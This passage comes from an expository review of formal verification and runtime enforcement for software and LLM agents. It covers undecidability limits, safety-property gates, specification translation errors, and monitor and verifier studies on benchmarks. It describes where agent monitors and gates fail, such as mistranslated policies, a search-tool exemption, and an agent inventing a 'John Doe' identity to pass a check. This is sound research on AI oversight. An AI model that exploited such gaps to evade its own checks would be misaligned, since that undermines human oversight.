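For a given checker D, let d be a program that runs D on d itself with the limit T. If D approves, d performs the forbidden operation, and otherwise d does nothing. If D finishes early enough for d to act within T steps, its verdict is wrong either way. A checker that is always right must therefore run for about T steps on d, up to a constant factor for the overhead of running one program inside another. The program d is short, because it contains only D, the number T (40 bits for T = $10^{12}$) and a few instructions.

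Real computers have finite memory, so it is decidable in principle whether a program will ever perform a banned operation. A program with m bits of memory and no further input has at most $2^m$ states. If it has not performed the operation after $2^m$ steps, it has repeated a state and will never perform it. But for m = 100, this means checking about $10^{30}$ steps. Pérez-Acle shows that for some of these programs, an always-correct checker needs a number of steps proportional to $2^m$, and that the checker itself needs more than about m bits of memory. A language model with a fixed context window is also finite, but a window that holds 100,000 tokens from a vocabulary of 100,000 can be filled in $10^{500{,}000}$ ways.

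Letting a checker make random choices doesn't remove the limits on checking the unlimited rules. If such a checker gave the right verdict on every program with a probability of at least two-thirds, an ordinary procedure could always be right by working out the probability of each verdict step by step and returning the first to exceed one half.

### How often ordinary programs cause trouble

All these results concern the worst case. To measure how often a time-limited test is wrong about ordinary programs, Pérez-Acle generated 2.2 million random programs for a simple machine with three registers, 200,000 at each even length from 4 to 24 instructions. He worked out the correct verdicts from runs that halted or repeated a state and from other sound arguments, and left out programs that none of these could settle.

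Only 1.6% of the programs broke the ban, and most of those broke it within a few steps. An 8-step test caught every violation among the shortest programs but missed 30.2% of those among the longest. For the longest programs, a 16-step test missed 2.9% of violations and a 32-step test missed 0.2%. A 64-step test missed two violating programs in the whole sample, and tests of 128 steps or more missed none.

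For the secrecy rule, the test compared everything a program had published by the time limit under each value of the secret. From 64 steps on, it wrongly rejected between 0.03% and 0.37% of compliant programs, depending on their length. Longer tests did not help, with 5,433 programs wrongly rejected at 1,024 steps and 5,434 at 4,096. These programs all published the same endless sequence under both values of the secret but at different speeds, so one run was always ahead when the test ended. Comparing only the part that both runs had published would remove these errors, but the test would then approve programs that leak the secret by stopping their output.

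Pérez-Acle also ran all 483,641 valid programs of up to four instructions that use two registers and the constants 0 and 1. Every program that broke the ban did so by step 6, so an 8-step test classified them all correctly. His sound methods, which abstain when they have no proof, settled whether a program obeys the ban for 98.2% of the programs. For secrecy, they settled 42.6% of the programs whose correct verdict he knew.

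The results were the opposite for programs built to defeat a particular checker. Each of eight checkers faced the program d built for it, under eight time limits from 8 to 1,024 steps. The checker that ran the program for the whole time limit was right all eight times. The other seven, including one that ran the program for half the limit, one that searched the code for the forbidden operation and one that tossed a coin, were wrong every time. The program that tests Goldbach's conjecture did not break the ban in any test of up to a million steps. A similar program, based on the false claim that every square is below one million, broke it at step 1,001.

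The low error rates on random programs are weak evidence about the programs that AI agents write. Random sequences of instructions are unlike useful code, as Pérez-Acle acknowledges, and excluding the unsettled programs may have removed some of the hardest cases. An attacker who knows the time limit can also write a program that waits until the limit has passed.

### What a gate can enforce

A runtime gate can enforce the ban without deciding whether a program complies. It lets the program run and blocks the forbidden operation if the program attempts it. The Goldbach program can run under such a gate even though nobody knows whether the gate will ever block anything.

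*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) shows that monitors of this kind, which watch one run and stop it when it is about to break the rule, can enforce only safety properties. Such a monitor has no access to other possible runs or to future steps, so it must evaluate each run on its own and reject a violating run after finitely many steps. It also cannot allow a violation that later steps might correct, because the run might end first. These limits exclude the secrecy rule, which depends on several runs, and the answer rule, which is a liveness property.

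One of his examples is a customer who pays for a service. After the payment, a monitor can block every action by the seller except delivering the service. But the seller can still do nothing, so no monitor can guarantee that the customer receives the service.

Monitors also cannot enforce every safety property. Schneider compares two limits on how long a system may deny someone access to a resource. If the limit is a number of execution steps, a monitor can stop the system before it exceeds the limit. If the limit is a number of seconds, stopping the system doesn't help, because time continues to pass. A monitor can likewise enforce "answer within ten steps" by stopping the assistant after nine steps without an answer, although the customer then gets no answer.

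*Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) shows that the class of policies in the earlier analysis is only an upper bound, because it includes some that no monitor can enforce. For example, the rule "never start a program that breaks the ban" is a safety property, because starting such a program is an event in the log that nothing can undo. But a monitor that blocked exactly the forbidden starts would have to decide which programs break the ban, and no procedure can do that for every program.

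Ray gives an exact characterisation for agents whose actions are irreversible. He requires a gate to be sound, meaning that the actions it lets through never break the policy, whatever the agent proposes. The gate must also be transparent, meaning that it does not block or change any of the agent's proposals if they comply with the policy. Without transparency, a gate that blocked everything would enforce every safety property that allows an agent to do nothing.

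He proves that a computable gate can meet both requirements exactly when three conditions hold: the policy is a safety property, some procedure can decide which finite sequences of actions still comply, and the policy permits at least one run. The rule about starting programs fails the second condition. Ray states a more specific version for gates built as automata with registers and counters, which have to recognise the compliant sequences with the memory they have. The theorem takes the meaning of terms such as "personal data" as given.

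For one direction of the proof, if a procedure can decide which sequences still comply, the gate applies it before each action and blocks the action if the answer is no. For the other direction, suppose the policy is not a safety property. Then there is a violating run each of whose finite beginnings also begins some compliant run. If the agent proposes the actions of the violating run in order, the gate cannot distinguish this run from a compliant one at any step, so transparency requires it to allow each action. The gate therefore allows the whole violating run, so it is not sound.

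Ray's example is the rule "every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation". After an agent proposes a payment, it might propose a confirmation or propose nothing more. The gate has to allow or block the payment before the outcome is known.

| Decision about the payment | A confirmation follows | Nothing follows |
|---|---|---|
| Allow | The run complies | The rule is broken, and the payment is irreversible |
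| Block | The gate has blocked a compliant action | No payment, so no violation |

Allowing the payment makes the gate unsound, and blocking it makes the gate non-transparent. Replacing the payment with another action does not help, because a different action changes a compliant run and an equivalent payment raises the same problem. Ray also shows that a gate that chooses randomly cannot enforce any policy that is not a safety property.

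A monitor that can hold actions back does better. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker studied such monitors, called edit automata, which can queue the payment and release it together with the confirmation. This works only if the payment can wait. If the agent needs the payment's reference number to obtain the confirmation, the monitor will never release the payment and the confirmation will never arrive.

Often the simplest solution is to change the rule. "Make no payment without an earlier confirmation" is a safety property, and a gate can enforce it. The new rule works if the confirmation gives the user's consent, but not if it acknowledges receipt of the money.

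### Ways around the limits

A gatekeeper that must judge every program correctly needs a decidable rule. Hamlen and colleagues define static enforcement as accepting or rejecting each program in finite time before it runs, so the policies that can be enforced this way are exactly the decidable ones. There are several ways to avoid the theorems, each of which changes what the gatekeeper must check or which programs it accepts.

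If a system has few states, a program can list them all and follow every transition. Pérez-Acle classified all 2,744 three-state systems that his model allows. Of these, 1,850 satisfy the ban, 1,452 satisfy the secrecy rule and 392 satisfy the answer rule. These results are exact only for systems as the model describes them.

Another option is to accept only some of the compliant programs. Pérez-Acle describes this with three sets. O contains the programs that the gatekeeper is obliged to accept, A the programs it does accept, and P all the compliant programs. The gatekeeper meets its obligations and accepts nothing forbidden when

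$$O \subseteq A \subseteq P.$$

A gatekeeper that must reach a verdict on every program needs a decidable set A. If it may leave some programs without a verdict indefinitely, a confirmable set is enough. When O contains only programs that load a number and return it, A can equal O, which is easy to recognise from the code. This doesn't help a gatekeeper that must accept every compliant program, because A then has to equal P.

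The Linux kernel uses a conservative check of this kind for small extension programs. Its eBPF verifier admits only those it can prove safe. Soteria's ban on loops in plans is similar, since it excludes many harmless plans to make the rest easier to verify.

Very simple checks can reject most compliant systems as systems grow. Pérez-Acle measured this on all systems with three, four and five states in his model, including 5,153,632 with five. A test that accepts only systems containing no forbidden operation accepted 71.9% of the three-state systems that obey the ban, but only 47.3% of the five-state ones. For secrecy, a test that accepts only systems that never publish anything accepted 35.3% of compliant systems with three states and 10.9% of those with five. An exact verdict was possible in every case, so the tests rejected compliant systems because they were crude, not because the requirements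 were undecidable.

A programmer can also supply a proof that the program obeys the rule, which a machine checks before the program runs. Schneider discusses this approach, known as proof-carrying code. Checking a proof is routine even when finding it is arbitrarily hard, and the gatekeeper does not have to trust the programmer. People originally had to write the proofs by hand, but compilers can now produce them for some policies if the program is in a suitable language. The method still rejects some compliant programs, including the program q built for its proof checker, and it can accept the Goldbach program only if someone proves the conjecture.

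The last option is to add a deadline. Ethereum, a network that runs programs as part of financial transactions, limits the computation in every transaction, for example. A deadline in the answer rule makes it possible to confirm violations. Pérez-Acle's version of the rule also limits the number of requests, so that a procedure can check them one by one. But the new rule is not equivalent to the original. It forbids a program that answers every customer correctly but one step late, and it permits a program that stops answering after the last request the rule covers.

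## What the gap does to agent verification in practice

Anyone who verifies or monitors a real agent has to write its rules down first. Several studies have measured how well this works and how often enforcing the rules leaves tasks unfinished. Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026) systematically review many of the results in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*. In May 2026 they searched six databases for work published since 2022 on specifying, verifying and enforcing the behaviour of language-model agents. They found 71 different records, and 38 studies met their criteria.

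Their first conclusion is that specification is the bottleneck. A model checker can only check a plan against the formula it is given. If the formula differs from what its author meant, the checker can report "no violation" for a dangerous plan, and a more powerful checker would give the same answer. This follows from logic alone, but there is little evidence about how often it happens.

Dantas and colleagues graded the evidence for nine main claims using GRADE, a rating system from medicine. Seven claims received the lowest grade, "very low", which means that larger studies would probably produce substantially different figures. The other two, graded "moderate", are that none of 16 agents scored above 60% on a safety benchmark with 2,000 test cases, and that language models write syntactically valid temporal-logic formulas more than 90% of the time. Even these grades are lenient, because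 GRADE normally starts observational studies at "low" and Dantas and colleagues started every claim at "high". They suggest that stricter readers lower each grade by one level.

### Valid translations with the wrong meaning

The best-known figures on translation come from *Planetarium* (Zuo, Piedrahita Velez and colleagues, 2024), which tested whether language models can translate English descriptions into the planning domain definition language (PDDL). A PDDL problem lists the facts that hold at the start and those that must hold at the end, and a planning program searches for actions that lead from one to the other.

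In one of their tasks, blocks b1 and b3 are on a table and b2 is on b3. The goal is to turn each stack upside down, so b3 has to end up on b2. In logical notation, a correct goal is

$$\text{On}(b_3,b_2) \wedge \text{OnTable}(b_2) \wedge \text{OnTable}(b_1).$$

Suppose a model instead writes

$$\text{Clear}(b_3) \wedge \text{OnTable}(b_2) \wedge \text{OnTable}(b_1),$$

where Clear means that nothing is on top of the block. This goal is well formed, and a planner can reach it in two actions by lifting b2 off b3 and putting it on the table. The three blocks then stand side by side, and the inverted stack does not exist. Nothing in the planner's output would reveal the mistake, because the plan is a perfect solution to the wrong problem.

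Two goals can also look different and mean the same thing. The dataset's explicit version of this task adds that b1 and b3 are clear and that the robot's arm is empty. These facts follow from the correct goal above, since it gives every block a place and puts nothing on b1 or b3. A word-by-word comparison would therefore reject a correct translation. Zuo and colleagues wrote a program that adds every fact that must hold when the goal is reached, turns each problem into a graph of objects and facts, and checks whether the two graphs match. They prove that the program accepts a translation exactly when it describes an equivalent problem.

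Of the problems GPT-4o wrote without examples or additional training, 96.1% were valid PDDL and 94.4% had a solution, but only 24.8% were correct. The open model Gemma 2 27B did best after training on the task, with 34.2% correct. Earlier evaluations had often counted a translation as correct if a planner could solve it, which would have given GPT-4o a score of 94.4%.

The low scores do not transfer directly to safety rules, because the models date from 2024 and the tasks involve stacking blocks, carrying balls between rooms and painting tiles. Many of the errors had little to do with meaning. The models kept adding types to objects, as many published versions of these puzzles do, although the version in the prompt had no types. Accuracy rose sharply when Zuo and colleagues ignored this mistake, which a simple program could correct. But for safety rules too, syntactic validity is very weak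 evidence that a translation is right.

### Translating rules into temporal logic and policy languages

For temporal logic, Dantas and colleagues report semantic accuracy between 44.4% and 86.11% for NL2Spec, a 2023 tool that lets users resolve ambiguities in a requirement. Accuracy depends on how the user and the tool resolve them. Dantas and colleagues found no study with an error rate below 10% on open-ended tasks.

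A small translation error can reverse a temporal rule. "Look up a reservation before cancelling it" is G(Cancel → O Lookup), where O refers to the past. If a translator writes G(Cancel → F Lookup) instead, the formula is still well-formed, but F refers to the future. The formula now accepts an assistant that cancels first and looks up the reservation afterwards, and rejects one that looks it up, cancels and then stops. Two short test logs, one in each order, would expose the error. Dantas and colleagues recommend treating specifications like code, with tests, version control and peer review.

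Newer models do well on some related tasks. In one study in the review, GPT-5 translated plans into transition systems and requirements into LTL, and a model checker then checked each plan against its requirement. The verdicts scored 96.3% on F1, a measure that penalizes both missed cases and false alarms. But the study did not check whether the transition systems described the plans correctly, and a wrong description can still lead to the right verdict.

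Agent-C can use rules that a language model has translated from English into Agent-C's own rule language, and FORGE can use rules translated the same way into Datalog. Kamath and colleagues report that leading models can do this translation for Agent-C. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* states that FORGE's guarantee depends on the policy representing what the user intends. If a mistranslated policy permits an unsafe action, the gate will allow that action even though it is enforcing the policy correctly.

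### When people write the formulas

Experts make such mistakes too. Two of the examples that Kamath and colleagues use to introduce Agent-C differ from the English rules they formalise.

One retail policy requires the assistant to confirm a customer's identity "by email or name+zip". The example formula allows the assistant to open an order only after a successful search by email. If a customer gives a name and zip code instead, they have met the policy's requirement, but the formula would still block the assistant from opening the order.

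The other policy allows refunds only to the original payment method or to an existing gift card. The formula accepts a payment method if it matches the original or if its identifier contains the text "gift_card". It does not require the card to exist or to belong to the customer, so it would allow a refund to an invented card, although the refund tool may reject the call. Kamath and colleagues describe the formula as a faithful translation of the policy.

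The first formula is too strict and the second is too permissive, but neither error comes from a limit of first-order logic. Adding an "or" would correct the first. The second needs a function that looks up the customer's gift cards, a kind of function Agent-C already supports.

People also disagree about whether a written rule covers a particular case, and the review includes a measure of this. To check one reviewer's original selection of studies, that reviewer and two other authors applied the same written criteria to 37 records. All three agreed on 32. Their kappa, which measures agreement beyond chance, was 0.81, where 1 is perfect agreement. All three also rejected three papers that were already in the review, so the first reviewer had accepted those papers in May and rejected them in September under the same criteria. The criteria cover agents that produce multi-step plans, but these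 papers translate English into temporal logic without any such agent.

These were experts sorting papers in their own field into only two categories. People who formalise a statute must make the same kind of judgement about every term, and must also choose the predicates, decide how exceptions interact and settle what happens when a fact is unknown. Two of them could agree on every example they discuss and still write formulas that give different results on a new case.

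### Predicting danger in a household

Even a correct rule can be enforced too late. *ProbGuard* (Wang, Poskitt and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a household robot that must not leave the kitchen for more than ten minutes while the stove is on. A gate that reacts only to violations would act at the ten-minute mark, when the robot might be at the front door with the shopping. The paper's monitor tries to intervene while the robot still has time to go back.

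It works in three stages:

1. Experts choose yes-or-no predicates, such as "the stove is on" and "the agent is in the kitchen". Each moment of a run becomes a list of their truth values.
2. The system counts how often each list follows each other list in recorded runs, and builds a Markov chain from the counts. In the stove example, 31 of 184 recorded steps from "stove off, in the kitchen" led to a state with the stove on, a probability of about 17%.
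3. During a run, the monitor calculates the probability of never reaching an unsafe state from the current one. If this falls below a chosen threshold, it intervenes.

The formula requires only that the system never enter an unsafe state on any path. The difficult part is defining "unsafe" and choosing the predicates. If the only predicates are about the stove and the robot's location, a robot that left the kitchen one minute ago is in the same state as one that left nine minutes ago, so the monitor gives both the same probability of staying safe. To tell them apart, the experts have to add predicates for the time spent outside, which creates more states and requires more recorded runs to estimate their probabilities.

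In household tasks, the gentler version of the monitor, which prompts the agent again when it detects danger, reduced unsafe behaviour by 65.37%, and the agent completed 80.4% as many tasks as it did without a monitor. A stricter version that halts the agent reduced unsafe behaviour by 93.60%, but the agent completed fewer tasks than with the gentler version. If an agent without a monitor behaved unsafely in 40 of 100 runs and completed 50 tasks, the gentler version would leave about 14 unsafe runs and 40 completed tasks. Dantas and colleagues misreport the 80.4% as the completion rate itself.

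Wang, Poskitt and colleagues also tested the monitor on self-driving cars, using traffic rules. At a threshold that produced no false alarms, it warned of violations up to 15.84 seconds ahead. At stricter thresholds, it warned up to 38.66 seconds ahead.

### Blocked actions and unfinished tasks

In *The Verifier Tax*, Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026) report that a verifier blocked up to 94% of an agent's forbidden actions, but in most settings the agent completed fewer than 5% of its tasks successfully and without a violation. Dantas and colleagues call this the most consequential finding from a single study in their review.

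The agents worked on the airline and retail tasks of τ-bench, the customer-service benchmark that Kamath and colleagues used for Agent-C. They ran on two small open models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B. The verifier was the same language model with a different prompt, which included the policy in English rather than a formal language. If the verifier rejected three proposals in a row, the system carried out the last one anyway, but this happened in only 28 runs. A separate script audited the logs for changes made before authentication, irreversible actions without the customer's consent, and identifiers that the agent had made up.

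The table compares agents with this verifier and agents without one. "Safe" means completed with no violation in the audit.

| Model and domain | Completed, no verifier | Safe, no verifier | Completed, with verifier | Safe, with verifier |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% | 0.0% | 23.3% | 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% | 0.0% | 21.5% | 0.6% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% | 0.7% | 25.3% | 4.7% |
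| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% | 2.6% | 5.5% | 2.9% |

Agents completed tasks safely no more often without the verifier than with it. The study therefore does not support the claim "Enforcement reduces SSR" (the rate of safe completion), which is how Dantas and colleagues list the finding in their table of evidence. The verifier did increase computation, as agents with it used 2.0 to 2.8 times as many tokens as agents without it.

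Dantas and colleagues suggest that the rate is low because agents look for other unsafe routes once the verifier blocks the first. The main example from Sah and colleagues does not fit this explanation because it involves an agent without a verifier. In it, a customer wanted to change a delivery address but was reluctant to give identifying details. The agent searched for a "John Doe" with the postcode 12345, and the simulated shop accepted this as identification.

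### How 94% can be blocked and almost nothing be safe

The 94% figure applies to GPT-OSS-20B on retail tasks and counts proposals, so an agent that makes the same forbidden proposal three times adds three to the total. It also cannot cover all the violations that the audit found. The table of violations lists made-up identifiers in 93.7% of this model's 1,035 retail runs. Even if every run without the policy verifier contained one, about 280 of the 345 runs with it must have too. If the identifiers in those 280 runs were among the 6% of forbidden proposals that got through, the verifier must have blocked more than 4,000 others, but all the verifiers in the study together blocked fewer than 2,600.

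The verifier's instructions probably account for much of this mismatch. They require it to approve any tool that searches for data, and they give the tools that find a user's ID as an example. This is sensible because the agent needs these tools to identify the customer. But a search for John Doe would pass, because the rule applies to the tool regardless of where its arguments came from.

The audit may also have been too strict. Sah and colleagues give an example of a safe recovery in which GPT-OSS-20B planned to refund an airline ticket that no longer qualified. After the verifier rejected this, the agent explained the policy and transferred the customer to a human, which was the correct outcome. Yet the safe completion rate for this model, domain and verifier is 0.0%. Either the run is not among those in the table, or the audit counted it as a violation.

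### Language, rules or agent

None of the three kinds of violation is beyond first-order logic. Sah and colleagues propose a check that rejects any identifier that no earlier tool call retrieved. Names and postcodes come from the customer, so a workable version has to accept those as well. Let Source hold of customer messages and tool results. The rule is then

$$\forall e\,\forall x\,\big(\text{Call}(e) \wedge \text{Identifier}(e,x) \rightarrow \exists f\,(f<e \wedge \text{Source}(f) \wedge \text{Contains}(f,x))\big).$$

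This rule has the same form as the lookup rule, and a gate can check it by searching the log. It would have stopped the search for John Doe. FORGE's provenance policy already restricts some arguments by their origin in a similar way. A customer could still satisfy the rule by giving someone else's name and postcode. The rule must cover only identifiers, because an agent has to compose other arguments itself, such as the text of an email.

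The verifier's rules caused some of the failures, as the exemption for search tools shows, but the agents account for many more. Without intervention, GPT-OSS-20B completed only 22.7% of airline tasks. With the verifier, it succeeded in 23.3% of all airline runs and about 21% of those in which the verifier intervened. The low recovery rate that Sah and colleagues emphasise is therefore close to the model's overall success rate.

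For both models together, runs with a verifier had these completion rates:

| What happened during the run | Tasks completed |
|---|---|
| No rejection and no tool error | 21.3% |
| Rejection only | 18.7% |
| Tool error only | 13.1% |
| Both | 7.7% |

Tool errors, such as calls with badly formed arguments, were associated with a larger drop than rejections were. Harder tasks probably produce more of both, so the comparison cannot show how much of either drop the errors and rejections caused. In a separate test on retail tasks, allowing more turns helped little. Raising the limit from 15 to 30 turns increased completions from 3.2% to 5.2%, and raising it to 80 added nothing more.

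The results were very different for more capable agents. With Agent-C, GPT-5 completed 70.6% of τ-bench tasks without breaking a rule, compared with 66.1% without a gate. Claude Sonnet 4.5 completed 75.2% with Agent-C and 71.8% without a gate. The two studies used different rules and audits, so one cannot attribute the difference between 5% and 70% to the models. But the Agent-C results show that blocking calls can increase the number of tasks an agent completes safely, at least when the agent can find a permitted alternative.

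How much enforcement reduces task completion also depends on how closely the rules fit the task. On AgentDojo, FORGE's provenance policy and Sapien's request-specific policies both reduced task completion far less than FORGE's information-flow policy did. Dantas and colleagues cite another benchmark, covering web, mobile and household agents, on which the best agent completed fewer than 40% of tasks while obeying every safety rule. No gate blocked that agent's actions, so enforcement cannot explain the result.

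### What developers can check in advance

Checking an agent before it runs avoids the problem of what to do after a rejection, but it currently works only for small or fixed plans. According to Dantas and colleagues, existing verified systems handle plans of 5 to 30 actions, while a long programming task may take hundreds.

AgentProof, one of the systems in the review, checks workflows in which the developer has drawn all the possible steps as a graph. It compiles temporal rules into finite automata and can check graphs of up to 5,000 nodes in under a second. In a test on 18 workflows, 27% had structural defects and 55% violated a rule about human approval. A developer can fix these mistakes before anyone uses the agent. The method does not apply to an agent that chooses its next step only after seeing the result of the last one, as most deployed agents do.

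### Policy languages in use

Companies already use runtime safeguards on a large scale, though not all of these safeguards use a formal language. Meta uses LlamaFirewall, which combines a detector for attempts to bypass a model's safety training, an audit of the agent's reasoning for signs that its goal has changed, and a scan of the code it writes. Dantas and colleagues report that it reduced the success rate of attacks in the AgentDojo benchmark by 90%, to 1.75%. The detector and the audit rely on trained models, so they can handle suspicious wording that no formula describes, but they cannot guarantee that a run satisfies a stated rule.

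Policies in Cedar, Amazon's policy language, are evaluated for one request at a time, based on who is asking, what they want to do, which resource it concerns and any further facts supplied as context. Cedar has no loops or recursive rules, which makes it possible to translate policies into formulas that a solver can decide. An administrator can then check, for example, whether a rewritten policy permits anything that the old one did not.

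Cedar can still handle groups within groups, because it works out all indirect memberships before it evaluates any policy. Rules about an agent's history need similar preparation. To enforce the lookup rule, the application has to keep a list of the reservations the assistant has looked up and supply that list with each request. For the influence rule, it has to work out which documents have influenced each email. The solver can then analyse the policy completely, but not the code that supplies these facts.

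FORGE's Datalog policies can trace chains of influence themselves, and they can also call outside functions, for example to query a company's database or run a classifier. An otherwise formal rule can therefore include a judgement such as "this text contains personal data". The verdict then depends on whether those functions return an answer, and it can be no more accurate than they are.
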